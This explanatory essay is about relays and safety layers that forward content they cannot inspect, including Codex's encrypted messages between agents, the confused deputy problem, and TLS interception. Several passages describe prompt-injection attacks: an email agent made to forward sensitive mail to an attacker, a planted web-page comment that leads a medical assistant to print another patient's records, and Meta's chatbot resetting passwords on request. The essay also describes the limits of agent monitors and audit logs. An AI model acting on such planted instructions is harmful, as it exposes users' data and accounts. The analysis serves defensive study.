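# Safety layers that must pass along content they cannot inspect

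## Relays, payloads and the confused deputy

A blind relay is a component that forwards messages it cannot read or understand. Examples include a mail server that carries encrypted email and a chat service that holds no key to its users' conversations. AI agents now contain blind relays too. An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by using tools to read files, run commands, search the web or send email on a person's behalf. The model only produces text. The software around it, known as the harness, sends it input, runs the tools it calls and records the session.

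The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), an issue brief from an association of AI developers, describes the harness as "a natural control point" for monitoring and enforcement, because an agent's actions pass through it. The harness can serve this purpose only to the extent that it can interpret what passes through. Some of the traffic in current agents is opaque to the harness, which must forward it anyway because the model uses it at the next step. What such a relay can guarantee depends on what it can still observe and on what the recipient can do with the message.

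### One turn of an agent's loop

Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent for a user's own computer, is a convenient example because its code is open. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) follows a request to add an architecture diagram to README.md, the file that introduces a software project. The turn runs as follows, with the permission check inserted where it occurs.

1. **User request.** The harness does not send the user's sentence alone. It sends a list that also holds descriptions of the available tools, standing instructions, a note on which files the agent may write to, and the current directory. All of this is plain text.
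2. **Model output.** OpenAI's servers run the model and send back two items. One records the model's reasoning: a short readable summary, and beside it a long encrypted string. The other is a tool call, which asks the harness to run the command `cat README.md` and so print the file.
3. **Permission gate.** A permission gate is a check that allows, refuses or refers to a person an action that an agent proposes. Here it has a short, legible command to judge.
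4. **Tool call.** The harness runs the command. Codex confines its own command-line tool to a sandbox, a restricted environment, but tools that come from outside servers have to enforce limits of their own.
5. **Tool result.** The text of the file comes back, and the harness labels it with the number of the call it answers. The harness can read the text, though anybody might have written it.
6. **Next model call.** The harness sends the whole list again with three items added at the end: the reasoning item with its encrypted string, the tool call and the result.

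The loop repeats until the model produces a message to the user instead of another tool call.

At step 6 the harness sends the encrypted string back to OpenAI, the only party that can decrypt it. The string makes this round trip because Codex makes every request self-contained, so OpenAI's servers don't need to retain the previous one. This suits customers with Zero Data Retention, an arrangement under which OpenAI does not store their data. OpenAI keeps the decryption key, and the customer's machine keeps the ciphertext (the encrypted text).

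Long sessions add another opaque item. When a conversation nears the limit of how much text the model can take in at once, Codex requests a shorter list from the server to replace it. The new list includes an encrypted item that, in Bolin's words, preserves the model's "latent understanding of the original conversation". From then on, the harness passes along part of the model's context as a string it cannot read.

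### Payload, envelope and encryption

The payload is the content of a message. The envelope is everything the relay can observe about the message: its sender, recipient, type, size, time and order. In the Codex example, the payload of the reasoning item is the underlying plaintext. Its envelope includes its source (OpenAI's server), the request it answered, its type ("reasoning"), its length, and its position right before a command to print a file. The readable summary is harder to classify because it accompanies the payload and purports to describe it, but the harness cannot compare the two.

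Which parts of a message count as envelope and which as payload depends on the observer. The harness reads the whole tool call, including the command. For a router between the user's computer and OpenAI, the entire exchange is normally encrypted, so the envelope is only addresses, sizes and times.

Systems that hide a payload commonly use authenticated encryption, which keeps the message secret and lets the recipient detect tampering. Someone without the key can learn almost nothing from the ciphertext except the message's approximate length. To make tampering detectable, the sender uses the key to compute a short tag from the message and attaches it. The recipient repeats the computation and rejects the message if the tags differ, as they will if even one bit has changed. A relay without the key therefore cannot read the message, alter it unnoticed or forge a new one, but it can still delay,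 drop or repeat what it carries. When the sender and recipient share one secret key, as is usual, the relay cannot check the tag either, so it may deliver a message that the recipient then rejects. A valid tag also does not show that the content is harmless, because anyone with the key can encrypt a malicious instruction and give it a valid tag.

### Four reasons for blindness

Encryption is only one way for a relay to end up blind, and the remedy differs with the cause.

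The Codex harness can only store and return the encrypted reasoning, because it lacks OpenAI's key. A harness that passes encrypted messages between agents is in the same situation.

In other cases, a component could read the content, but a rule forbids it. Suppose a company routes its employees' email agents through a logging server, and company policy allows the server to record senders, recipients and sizes but not to open the messages. The server holds the text in memory, so it could quickly start reading the messages if the policy were changed or broken. Zero Data Retention is similar but not identical, since it restricts what OpenAI keeps after a request, not what its servers process during one. The Frontier Model Forum lists among its open problems how to keep agents' behaviour visible without compromising users' privacy, so the conflict behind such rules is far from settled.

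Designers may also keep content from a component on purpose. Claude Code, the coding agent of the AI company Anthropic, has an "auto mode" in which a classifier, a model that sorts its input into categories, approves or blocks tool calls in place of a person. According to Anthropic, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not Claude's own messages or the tools' outputs, which makes it "reasoning-blind by design". A separate probe screens the tool outputs for attacks. The classifier's fast first stage answers with a single token, the smallest unit of text a model produces, and only the actions it flags go on to a slower stage that reasons at length. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans use auto mode by default from 14 August 2026.

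Finally, a relay may have access to every byte and still be unable to interpret them. A gate that monitors an agent launching a downloaded program can copy the whole compiled file without determining what it will do, and text in an unfamiliar encoding poses the same problem. People who approve commands by hand face it too. In the newsletter piece *Claude Code*, Hightower (2026) describes approving an eight-line command "full of what looks like line noise". This is a commentator's anecdote, not a measurement, though arguably anyone who has worked at a command line will recognise it. This kind of difficulty is a matter of degree, and a decoder, a more capable model or an hour's patience may overcome it, but skill at reading cannot make up for a missing decryption key.

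### Prompt injection

A relay can be unsafe even when it can read the whole payload. The tool result at step 5 was legible, and tool results are the usual route for prompt injection, in which an agent follows text in the material it processes as if it were an instruction from its user. The Frontier Model Forum gives the example of an email from an unknown sender with hidden instructions. The user's email agent reads the message, collects sensitive mail from the inbox and forwards it to the attacker. The Forum calls this indirect prompt injection. It also counts a direct form, in which the user types the malicious text and tries to override the instructions of whoever runs the system.

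Codex labels each item in its list with a role that indicates how much weight the model should give the content. The model may still fail to tell instructions from data, because it takes in labels and content as one sequence of tokens. In ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks*, a spokesman for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) explains that inside a language model "there is only ever 'next token'", with no built-in distinction between data and instructions. He contrasts this with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent that attack by sending the command and the data to the database separately. He warns that prompt injection may never be completely fixed.

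The NCSC's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* recommends that defenders treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". The phrase goes back to an incident in the 1970s in which a billing file was lost.

### Hardy's compiler

A confused deputy is a program that is led to use its own authority on behalf of a party that lacks it. The name comes from *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 paper by Norm Hardy, an operating system designer. The paper describes a fault he had encountered about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Hardy calls it "a nearly true story", with inessential details changed.

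Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory named SYSX. Customers who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. Hardy's team had also set up the compiler to collect statistics on how people used the programming language and write them to a file named STAT in SYSX. To let it write there, the team gave it a "home files license", which allowed a program to write to files in its own directory.

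SYSX also held BILL, the file with the company's billing information. A customer learned the file's name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for the debugging output. The compiler then asked the operating system to open BILL for writing, and the operating system allowed this because the compiler had its license. The debugging output overwrote the billing information. Hardy does not mention whether the customer meant any harm.

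He then goes through the obvious repairs, none of which works. The compiler could refuse file names outside the customer's own directory, but customers have good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse anything in SYSX, but the code predates that directory's name, and somebody with proper access to SYSX might well want output there. It could refuse BILL in particular, but somebody would then have to revise the compiler each time another sensitive file arrived. Tymshare's rule for when a program may open a file grew until it contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s. The code for the debugging output was correct when it was written, but it became wrong when the compiler received its license, although nobody had changed it.

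The confusion lies in the compiler's request to open the file for debugging output. The compiler had authority from two sources, the customer who ran it and its own license. It was supposed to use the license to write statistics and the customer's authority to write debugging output. But the request contained only a file name, so the compiler could not specify which authority it was using, and the operating system accepted whichever was sufficient. As a result, the compiler's license allowed it to open the file the customer had chosen. Tymshare first added a system call that let a program "switch hats" between its two authorities, but soon found programs that needed more than two. Hardy came to prefer capabilities, which are unforgeable references that both name a resource and grant the right to use it.

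The compiler could read all ten characters of the file name, but they did not show whether the sender had the right to make the request, which was the one fact that mattered. The same characters would have been a proper request from an employee entitled to write to that file, so a closer reading would not have helped.

### The same fault in AI systems

The security firm Quarkslab recreated Hardy's situation with a language model in the middle. It built a medical assistant with a tool that took a patient's number from the model and returned that patient's records. Logged in as patient 1, the testers asked for someone else's history and got it. They then added a line to the assistant's standing instructions that limited it to the logged-in patient, and the same request failed. Next they gave the assistant a web page about a diabetes study, with a comment in the page's source containing a request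 for everything on patient 2, and the assistant printed the records.

Changing the tool did work. Once it compared the requested number with the logged-in user's identity, the injected comment led to a refusal even under the original, weaker instructions. The testers used Claude 3 Haiku, a model from 2024, so their success with the hidden comment is poor evidence of how often such text misleads current models, but the flaw in the tool does not depend on the model.

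A much larger case came to light in the spring of 2026 at Meta, the owner of Instagram. According to Reuters' *High-profile Meta AI chatbot breach spotlights security risks of automation*, the company had launched an AI support chatbot in March for users who had lost access to their accounts or faced mistaken penalties. A user could ask it to email a password-reset link. Meta's *Incident Notification* (2026), a letter to Nebraska's attorney general, says the system did not properly verify that the address a person supplied was the one on file for the account. It sent the link to the supplied address, and the recipient could set a new password and log in unless the account's owner had turned on two-factor authentication.

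*Data Breach Notices* (Office of the Maine Attorney General, 2026) dates the breach to 17 April and its discovery to 31 May, and lists 20,225 people as affected. *In AI blunder, more than 34,000 Instagram accounts were attacked* (Isaac and Tan, 2026) cites internal documents that list roughly 34,000 affected accounts, of which about 20,000 were breached and more than 3,500 lost their user names. The figure of 20,225 may be somewhat high, since Meta calls its count for Nebraska an upper bound that could include logins by rightful owners. The victims included Barack Obama's dormant White House account and a senior US Space Force official.

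The Meta case closely parallels Tymshare. Meta's system had the authority to reset passwords across Instagram, while each requester had authority over one account at most. The requester supplied an email address, as Hardy's customer had supplied a file name, and the system acted on it with its own authority.

Accounts differ on how far the AI was at fault. Experts who spoke to Reuters classed the attack as prompt injection, and one of them, Brian Westnedge of the security company Red Sift, said that the model had received "privileged actions without privileged access controls". Meta maintains that the tool "worked properly and functioned as intended" and that the bug was in a separate code path. The company has an obvious interest in that version, and the public has little besides its word for it. If Meta is right, the incident is an even clearer case of a confused deputy, because nobody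 had to deceive the model. Whittaker (2026), in *Meta confirms thousands of Instagram accounts were hacked*, reports that attackers had a verification code sent to their own address "simply by asking". A more cautious model might have refused some of these requests, but comparing two email addresses would have stopped every request of this form, and that check was missing on either account.

### Four positions

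The compiler and the support system both failed with the message in plain sight. A blind relay has the same difficulty in telling who is entitled to ask for what, and it lacks the text as well. There are four main positions on what to do about this:

- **Inspect the content.** The harness, or a monitor (a program, model or person that watches an agent's messages or actions for signs of harm), should be able to read whatever passes and stop what looks dangerous.
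- **Hide it from every intermediary.** Each component that can read a message can also leak or alter it, so only the endpoints should hold the keys.
- **Isolate it by design.** The model that decides on actions should never take in untrusted content, so that no payload can redirect it.
- **Check it by cryptography or secure hardware.** Mathematical proofs or protected processors should establish particular facts about a hidden payload without revealing it to the relay.

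## Encrypted messages between coding agents in OpenAI's Codex

In June 2026 OpenAI changed Codex so that the harness on a developer's computer could no longer read the tasks that one agent gives another. Codex already carried encrypted reasoning and encrypted conversation summaries, but the newly hidden text consists of instructions, and the agent that receives them can run commands on the developer's machine.

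Codex can divide a large job among several agents. The parent agent, which talks to the user, starts subagents that each have their own conversation with the model. One might revise an interface while another writes tests, and the parent assembles the results. The parent has three tools for handing out work: `spawn_agent` creates a subagent with a first task, `send_message` gives it further information, and `followup_task` gives it more to do. Codex used to store the messages sent through all three tools as plain text in the local session log.

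*The Multi-Agent Auditability Gap* (Vaughan, 2026), a post on a personal blog about Codex, dates the change to 5 June, when OpenAI merged code edits titled "Encrypt multi-agent v2 message payloads". Users received it three days later in version 0.138.0. It affected only MultiAgentV2, the newer of Codex's two systems for coordinating agents. On 14 July, version 0.144.4 made MultiAgentV2 the default for GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.6 Terra, and from then on developers using those models could not avoid the encryption. According to The Decoder's *OpenAI's Codex now encrypts instructions between AI agents*, messages stayed readable for Luna, the smallest GPT-5.6 model. The older GPT-5.5 for a time ignored the setting that should have turned encryption off, but OpenAI has apparently since moved it back to readable messages.

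### The path of one task

The July 2026 article *Codex Is Still Open Source* gives a sample task: "Review the authentication changes and report regressions." Before Codex encrypted messages between agents, a developer could find that sentence in the local log, but afterwards the same field held ciphertext. Because the harness code is public, the article can trace the message from one end to the other.

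The parent's model, running on OpenAI's servers, writes the sentence as part of a `spawn_agent` call. The Responses API, through which Codex uses OpenAI's models, encrypts the sentence before the call leaves the servers. The harness receives the call with a ciphertext in place of the text, and stores it. To start the subagent, the harness opens a second series of model calls and includes the same ciphertext. OpenAI's servers decrypt it and give the sentence to the subagent's model. After that, the loop runs as it does for any agent, with readable commands and results.

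The message travels from OpenAI back to OpenAI through a computer whose owner cannot read it. Amazon Web Services' guidance *AGENTSEC06-BP01 Encrypt and sign inter-agent messages* also recommends encrypting messages between agents, but with separate keys for each "trust zone" and signatures that the receiving agent checks before it acts. A company that follows this advice with its own keys can give one to its auditors, but a Codex customer can't because it has no key.

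The Decoder reports that several developers described handoffs failing because OpenAI's side could not decrypt the task, in some cases even though the parent and subagent used the same model. Because the harness lacks the key, it cannot test a ciphertext before sending it or repair it afterwards.

### What the harness can still read

OpenAI's documentation for Multi-agent, a hosted service in which OpenAI's servers coordinate the agents and the developer's application runs the tools, shows the message format. Each agent's name is a path, such as `/root/reviewer/tester`, that shows which agent created which. The record of a `spawn_agent` call gives the action, the agent that made the call, the name of the task and a setting called `fork_turns`, which determines how much of the parent's conversation the subagent inherits. The message itself is a string that begins with "enc_".

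The local Codex client and the hosted service differ in a few places, chiefly in what happens to a subagent's reply.

| Part of the record | What the developer's side holds |
|---|---|
| Creation of a subagent | Plain text |
| Author, recipient, action and task name | Plain text in the hosted service's format |
| Tool calls and shell commands | Plain text |
| Results of tools and commands | Plain text |
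| Text of a task or follow-up message | Ciphertext |
| Subagent's reply to its parent | Plain text in local Codex, ciphertext in the hosted service |
| Model's reasoning | Ciphertext; the hosted service offers no readable summary with Multi-agent |
| Summary of older conversation | Ciphertext |

The envelope contains a lot of information, but it does little to narrow down what a subagent might do. In the hosted service, every agent can use all the tools the developer configured for the request, so a subagent whose task name suggests a small job has the same tools as its parent. OpenAI sets no fixed limit on how many subagents a run may create or how deeply they may be nested, although by default only three work at once. A task may therefore pass down through several agents, with a new ciphertext at each step.

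Delegation does not require this secrecy. The older Codex system still works with readable tasks, and OpenAI's *Agents*, the technical reference for its managed cloud agents, defines the content that agents exchange as either plain text or encrypted.

### Summaries of long conversations

The encrypted summaries that replace the older part of a long conversation make the same round trip. When Multi-agent is on, OpenAI's servers produce them automatically, even if the developer has not requested them, and summarize the root agent's conversation and each subagent's separately. Developers can change how long a conversation gets before it is summarized, but they cannot read the summaries.

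Suppose a user writes at the start of a long session that no agent may touch the billing tests. Two hours later, the servers condense that part of the conversation. A developer who has kept the full log can still read the original instruction, but cannot read the summary to check whether it includes the instruction. If the parent agent then delegates work, it uses the summary to write a task, which the developer also cannot read. The instruction could have been lost in either the summary or the task.

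### A deleted file

Suppose the user asks Codex to remove unused test data, and a subagent deletes `customers.csv`, which the billing tests need.

The developer can reconstruct much of what happened from the local log. It records when the parent created the subagent, the commands the subagent ran before the deletion, the deletion command, and the report the subagent sent back. If the subagent searched for uses of the file in the wrong folder, the commands alone may reveal the mistake. If it read a file with a planted instruction to delete `customers.csv`, the developer can find that text too.

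The log does not settle whether the subagent did what it was told. At least three histories would leave much the same record:

- The parent named `customers.csv` in the task, and the subagent obeyed.
- The parent passed on the user's request correctly, and the subagent picked the wrong file.
- The parent had read a web page with a hidden instruction and copied it into the task.

If a web page planted the instruction, the developer might find the page among the parent's tool results but could not confirm that the parent passed the instruction on. Each cause needs a different response. A parent that delegates badly needs better standing instructions, and a subagent that misreads a sound task may need a stronger model, whereas a planted instruction is a security incident that may have affected other sessions. In an account of how it runs Codex internally, OpenAI writes that it keeps logs to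 "understand and audit what the agent did". A Codex customer can still do most of that, but cannot audit what the parent asked the subagent to do.

Some problems would cause no visible failure to investigate. Vaughan raises the possibility that a parent copies a password or an internal address into a task, where the customer's security team cannot find it and would not know to look. OpenAI's servers had already processed the secret as part of the parent's conversation, which limits the harm, but the subagent now has it too and might use its tools to send it elsewhere.

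Developers have a few partial substitutes. They can instruct every subagent to restate its task before starting, which produces a readable account, but the subagent may have misunderstood the task. They can repeat the job with Luna, or try to switch MultiAgentV2 off, but a second run may well delegate the work differently. Vaughan also advises setting Codex to ask for approval before it creates a subagent, on the grounds that the approval prompt contains the text before encryption. This seems inconsistent with the fact that encryption happens on OpenAI's servers, which leaves the harness with no plain text to put in a prompt. *Codex Is Still Open Source* also found a further code change that removed the previews of encrypted tasks.

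The deletion command, unlike the task, is readable before it runs. *Inside the Codex sandbox* (Bolin, 2026) describes file and network limits that can still apply to the command, and *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes a separate agent that can still review it. But neither a person nor a local program can compare the command with the task that led to it.

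### Issue 28058

Ignat Remizov, chief technology officer of the payment service Zolvat, filed a complaint on 13 June under the username ignatremizov, as issue 28058 on GitHub, which hosts Codex's code. In the complaint, *Regression*, Remizov classed the loss of the readable audit trail as a fault introduced by the update. Remizov asked for a readable copy of each task, stored locally beside the encrypted one, but did not ask OpenAI to give up encryption.

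OpenAI has given little response. Vaughan reports second-hand that an OpenAI contributor declined the changes because "the protocol remains under development". Two days later, on 27 July, Vaughan (2026) described the issue as open and without an official response. The two accounts can both be true if the contributor was not speaking for the company, and neither includes a reason from OpenAI for the encryption. Version 0.145.0, released on 21 July, included work to stabilise MultiAgentV2.

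In late November 2026, OpenAI's Multi-agent documentation, which by then also covered the GPT-6.2 models, still showed messages between agents as ciphertext. This is evidence about the hosted service, but it doesn't establish whether the local client's logs have changed.

### Possible reasons for the encryption

OpenAI has confirmed the change but not its purpose, so every explanation is conjecture.

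Many developers suspect that OpenAI wants to stop rivals from copying its models. A developer can train a weaker model on a stronger one's output, a technique called distillation, and examples of how a strong model divides up a job would be useful for that. The Decoder finds the suspicion plausible and mentions similar suspicions about GLM-5.2, an open model from the Chinese company Zhipu AI. OpenAI encrypts the tasks of the two larger GPT-5.6 models and leaves those of the smallest readable, which is consistent with this motive. But a company introducing a new protocol in stages might do the same, and OpenAI leaves the subagents' commands and results in plain text, though they would also make good training data.

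The Decoder considers data retention an equally likely explanation. OpenAI may be handling tasks the same way as encrypted reasoning, which customers' machines already store for it. That would explain why a task passes through the customer's computer, but not why the customer can't read it, since Codex sends the user's messages and tool results in plain text under the same arrangement.

A third group of guesses concerns protocol design. *Codex Is Still Open Source* mentions message integrity and a wish to bring Codex into line with OpenAI's hosted service. Integrity alone is a weak reason for hiding the text, because a readable task with a tag that only OpenAI can compute would prevent malicious software on the developer's machine from rewriting the task unnoticed just as well as authenticated encryption would. Compatibility with the hosted service is a more convincing explanation for the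 local change, but it doesn't explain why the hosted service encrypts its messages.

### The proposal for a readable copy

Remizov built a modified version of Codex to demonstrate the idea. According to Vaughan's *Encrypted Subagent Delegation* (2026), this version adds a second, unencrypted task field to each of the three delegation tools. The harness saves that field in its logs, but the subagent receives only the ciphertext. Users can choose encrypted messages, encrypted messages with a readable copy, or plain text.

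Vaughan calls the design sound because encrypted delivery and a readable log are "orthogonal". That depends on why OpenAI encrypts the messages. A readable copy on the customer's own machine doesn't interfere with encryption meant to avoid storing customers' data or to stop tampering. But if the aim is to keep rivals from collecting the tasks, the copy defeats it, because rivals could collect the copies instead. OpenAI would then have reason to refuse the feature even if it worked well.

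The harness also cannot produce the readable copy itself, because it never has the plain text of the encrypted task. The copy has to arrive separately, presumably because the parent model writes the task twice, once for each field, and the harness cannot check that the two versions match. The model might shorten or reword the readable version. A parent influenced by a planted instruction could write a harmless sentence for the log and send something else to the subagent. The modified Codex also limits payloads to 8 KiB, or roughly 8,000 characters of English, to keep the logs from growing without bound, so a long task could be a problem even for an honest parent.

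This may not matter much for ordinary debugging, because a parent agent that makes a mistake will probably write the same faulty task in both fields, and the developer will see it. The copy is least reliable when someone has manipulated the parent, which is when an investigator would need it most.

The encrypting service could close the gap, since it has both the plain text and the ciphertext. It would make the copy itself, without involving the model, and attest that the copy matches the ciphertext. To do this, it would compute a hash of each, a short fingerprint that changes if the text changes, and sign both hashes together with the identity of the session and the recipient. The harness could verify the signature using a public key from OpenAI. A valid signature would rule out alteration by anyone else, but the developer would still have to trust OpenAI that the copy and the ciphertext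 match.

OpenAI could remove even that reliance by releasing the key for the individual message. The harness would then encrypt the copy itself and check that it gets the same ciphertext. This check is reliable only if the encryption scheme prevents a ciphertext from decrypting to different messages under different keys. But the encryption would no longer hide anything from the customer, so it would be simpler to avoid the comparison by sending only one readable task with a tag, logging it, and having OpenAI's servers check the tag when the task comes back.

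The customer could also do without a copy. It already stores the ciphertext, so after an incident it could send the relevant messages to OpenAI for decryption, if OpenAI still had the key. This would protect the tasks from bulk collection and still let an investigator read the one that preceded a deletion. However, the customer would depend on OpenAI's cooperation when OpenAI's model might be at fault. OpenAI's documentation for Multi-agent describes no such procedure.

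### What the law requires

The dispute has a legal side because Article 12 of the EU AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to "technically allow for the automatic recording of events" throughout their lifetime. This requirement was due to apply to the uses listed in Annex III from 2 August 2026. According to Vaughan, an amendment on which EU negotiators reached political agreement in May 2026 postponed it to 2 December 2027. Violations can then bring fines of up to €15 million or 3% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher.

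Article 12 requires a level of traceability appropriate to the system's purpose, with logs that help people identify risks and monitor how the system operates. Vaughan interprets it more strictly than its wording, as requiring a complete chain from input to output, and concludes that Codex falls short. The article prescribes particular log contents, such as the input data that led to a match, only for remote biometric identification. It does not mention messages between agents, so a company could argue that a log of commands and results is enough. That argument would be weaker if a hidden task were the most likely cause of a harmful outcome.

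The provider, which develops a system or puts it on the market under its own name, must build in the logging. Both the provider and the deployer, the organisation that uses the system in its work, must keep any logs they control for at least six months.

Most developers who use Codex are probably outside these rules. Annex III covers uses such as screening job applicants, assessing people's credit and operating critical infrastructure, but not writing software. The Act classifies a system by its own intended purpose, and medical firmware is a separate product with its own rules, so Vaughan seems too quick to call it "straightforward" that a coding tool is high-risk when a team uses it for such firmware or for financial systems.

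A clearer case would be a company that builds an applicant-screening product on OpenAI's hosted Multi-agent service. The company would be the provider. If one of its agents told another how to rank candidates, the company's log would contain that instruction only as ciphertext. Article 25 requires such a provider and its supplier to specify in a written agreement what information and technical access the provider needs to comply. The company would therefore have a legal basis for asking OpenAI for readable tasks, and if it could not get them, it might have to coordinate its agents some other way. The duties do not yet apply, so no court has had to decide whether a company has a log "under its control" when somebody else holds the key.

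## The case for inspecting content in transit

A company whose agents pass each other instructions in ciphertext can require a safety layer that reads whatever it forwards and blocks anything it cannot read. Enterprise network defenders, auditors and many developers who monitor agents favour some version of this rule. They argue mainly that metadata rarely distinguishes harmful traffic from ordinary traffic. A nightly backup and a theft of customer records can have the same sender, size and destination, so a relay that sees only this metadata must allow both or block both.

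Companies have applied this reasoning to their own networks for years. Most web traffic now uses Transport Layer Security (TLS), the protocol that encrypts HTTPS connections between browsers and websites. The dispute over whether companies may decrypt those connections is the longest test so far of the case for inspection.

### How a middlebox opens an encrypted connection

A middlebox is a device on the network path that inspects, filters or changes traffic between two endpoints. TLS is meant to keep it out. A website proves its identity with a certificate, a signed statement that a certain public key belongs to a certain domain, and the browser accepts the certificate only if the signature leads back to one of the root authorities that the device trusts. No reputable authority would sign a certificate that lets a company's middlebox pose as somebody else's site, so the company adds an authority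 of its own. Durumeric, Ma and colleagues (2017), in *The Security Impact of HTTPS Interception*, describe how this works:

1. **Installed root.** An administrator puts the middlebox's own root certificate on every computer in the organisation.
2. **First session.** An employee's browser tries to connect to a webmail site, and the middlebox answers in the site's place. It generates a certificate for that domain on the spot and signs it with its own root. The browser finds the root on its list and accepts.
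3. **Second session.** The middlebox opens a separate TLS connection to the real site, where it plays the part of the browser.
4. **Inspection.** The middlebox decrypts the employee's request with the keys of the first session and scans the plain text for malware or confidential data. It then blocks the request or encrypts it again with the keys of the second session. Replies take the same route backwards.

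Few employees will notice the interception, since they would have to open the certificate and check who signed it. Some browsers can "pin" a site, which means accepting only particular keys for it, but Chrome, Firefox and Safari skipped the pinning check when the certificate chained to a locally installed root certificate. Many antivirus programs intercept connections in the same way on the user's machine.

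The middlebox is now an endpoint of two sessions, one with the browser and one with the real site. The browser has no access to the second session, so if the middlebox fails to check the site's certificate, it goes unchecked.

### The dispute over TLS 1.3

Many companies preferred passive decryption inside their data centres, which leaves the connection intact. A monitoring device receives a copy of the traffic and decrypts it with a copy of the server's private key. This worked with RSA key exchange, an older method of agreeing on keys in which the browser chose a secret and sent it encrypted with the server's long-term public key. Anyone with the matching private key could recover the secret from a recording of the traffic, even years later.

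With RSA key exchange, anyone who held the server's private key could decrypt recorded traffic. This helped auditors, but it also helped thieves who recorded traffic and stole the key later. Forward secrecy prevents a stolen key from decrypting past sessions. TLS 1.3, published in 2018, dropped RSA key exchange and made ephemeral Diffie-Hellman, which provides forward secrecy, its main method.

In Diffie-Hellman, the two sides share a public number `g` and a large prime `p`. The client picks a secret number `a` and sends `g^a mod p`, and the server picks a secret `b` and sends `g^b mod p`. Each side raises the value it received to the power of its own secret, so both get `g^(ab) mod p` and derive the session's keys from it. An eavesdropper sees the two transmitted values but has no practical way to compute the shared one. In ephemeral Diffie-Hellman, both sides pick fresh secrets for each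 session and then discard them, so there is no long-lived key to give to a monitoring device.

Banks objected to TLS 1.3 while the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which maintains TLS, was still drafting it. Andrew Kennedy worked for BITS, the technology policy division of a US association of financial companies. In *Industry Concerns about TLS 1.3*, an email to the IETF's TLS working group, Kennedy (2016) wrote that the law requires banks to keep retrievable records of certain employees' communications. Kennedy argued that a bank can fire an employee who evades its monitoring but remains liable for the missing record. In another message in the thread, Kennedy described the dispute as one security requirement "in conflict with a different security requirement".

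The following year, *Data Center use of Static Diffie-Hellman in TLS 1.3* (Green, Droms and colleagues, 2017) proposed a way to restore passive decryption. The server would use the same `b` for every connection and share it with authorised monitoring devices. A device that had recorded `g^a` could then raise it to the power `b` to obtain the session's secret, just as the server does. Browsers would need no changes. The proposal calls this a "deliberate weakening of some security properties", because anyone who stole `b` could decrypt every session that had used it.

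Green and colleagues also explain why they found the alternatives wanting:

- **Packet headers.** Addresses and other unencrypted headers do not let an engineer find one customer's failed transaction, which requires user names, session numbers or web addresses from the payload. Security teams likewise search payloads for known signs of an intrusion.
- **Server logs.** Programmers cannot foresee every fault and put a log message in the right place.
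- **Exported session keys.** A large company would have to store billions of keys and get each one to its monitoring tools in time.
- **Inline middleboxes.** Each one adds cost, delay and another device that can break the service.

Fenter (2020), in *TLS 1.3 Operational Challenges*, sums up the demand as the ability to trace a packet anywhere in the enterprise and decrypt it. Fenter, who co-wrote the 2017 proposal, illustrates the problem by showing a failed login first encrypted and then decrypted.

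The Electronic Frontier Foundation (EFF), a digital rights group, answers that a company can log the data on its own servers. Server logs can also leave out passwords, whereas a decrypted recording contains everything. The EFF worries more that public websites would adopt the weaker method, by choice or by accident, and expose billions of people's data.

Both sides are partly right about logging. A company can log the events it knows it must account for, but a fault that nobody foresaw may have left its only trace in the packets. Kennedy's record-keeping example gives the 2017 proposal little support. If a broker sends messages through an outside website, the bank doesn't hold that server's key, so with any version of TLS it needs an interception middlebox or software on the broker's computer to read them.

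### The enterprise variant

According to the EFF, the IETF decided against standardising the proposal, and BITS took it to ETSI, a European standards body. ETSI published a variant called eTLS in October 2018. ETSI (2018) announced it as "created by industry, for industry" and listed compliance, troubleshooting and detecting attacks among its purposes. The IETF objected to the TLS name, and ETSI renamed the variant Enterprise Transport Security.

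ETSI's *Middlebox Security Protocol* (2019) follows the 2017 proposal but adds a notice. The server's certificate must include a fingerprint of the reused key and a readable description of who may hold copies of it. The client can therefore learn of the inspection, an opportunity that an ordinary interception middlebox does not offer. However, a standard TLS 1.3 client connects as usual despite the notice unless somebody has added support for reading it. An optional version omits the notice if the company has informed users another way, such as in its rules for using the network.

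ETSI concedes that the TLS 1.3 variant lacks forward secrecy until every copy of the reused key has been destroyed. It recommends the variant for traffic inside an organisation and normal TLS 1.3 for outside connections, and lets each company decide how often to change the key. ETSI defends the compromise by arguing that companies with no way to inspect TLS 1.3 might block it at the gateway, pushing their users back to older, weaker versions.

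The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) later looked for ways to avoid that outcome. Souppaya, Wells and colleagues (2025) worked with technology companies to build several demonstration systems, described in *Addressing Visibility Challenges with TLS 1.3 within the Enterprise*. The systems comply with TLS 1.3 and support monitoring in real time and after the event. Newhouse (2025) published the final guide under the same title in September 2025, and NIST's *Now Available* describes its subject as application servers in data centres that the enterprise controls. The result therefore does not support reading traffic between two parties who are both strangers to the inspector.

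Preuß Mattsson (2024), in a reply headed *NIST* on the TLS working group's mailing list, did not welcome the project and insisted that any visibility must come from the endpoints, with authentication and as little accessible data as possible.

Staying on TLS 1.2 is becoming less practical. In July 2026 the IETF issued a revised standard for TLS 1.3, announced in *RFC 9846 on The Transport Layer Security (TLS) Protocol Version 1.3* (2026). *New Protocols Using TLS Must Require TLS 1.3* (Salz and Aviram, 2026) set that requirement the same month. Companies may still run TLS 1.2, but it will receive no new features (Bortzmeyer, 2026, *RFC 9851 : TLS 1.2 is in Feature Freeze*). According to NIST, quantum-resistant algorithms are arriving with TLS 1.3, so a company that keeps TLS 1.2 to preserve its monitoring will miss them.

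### What interception did to real connections

Durumeric and colleagues measured how common interception was and how it affected security. To detect it, they checked whether the browser named in a connection matched the software that had opened it. When a client opens a TLS connection, it sends a list of the encryption methods and extensions it supports, in an order that differs between programs. The browser also identifies itself in a line of text called the User-Agent header, which middleboxes commonly pass along. If the header names Chrome but the opening message lists something Chrome has never supported, another program must have made the connection. One such sign was an extension called heartbeat, which none of the four main browsers had ever used.

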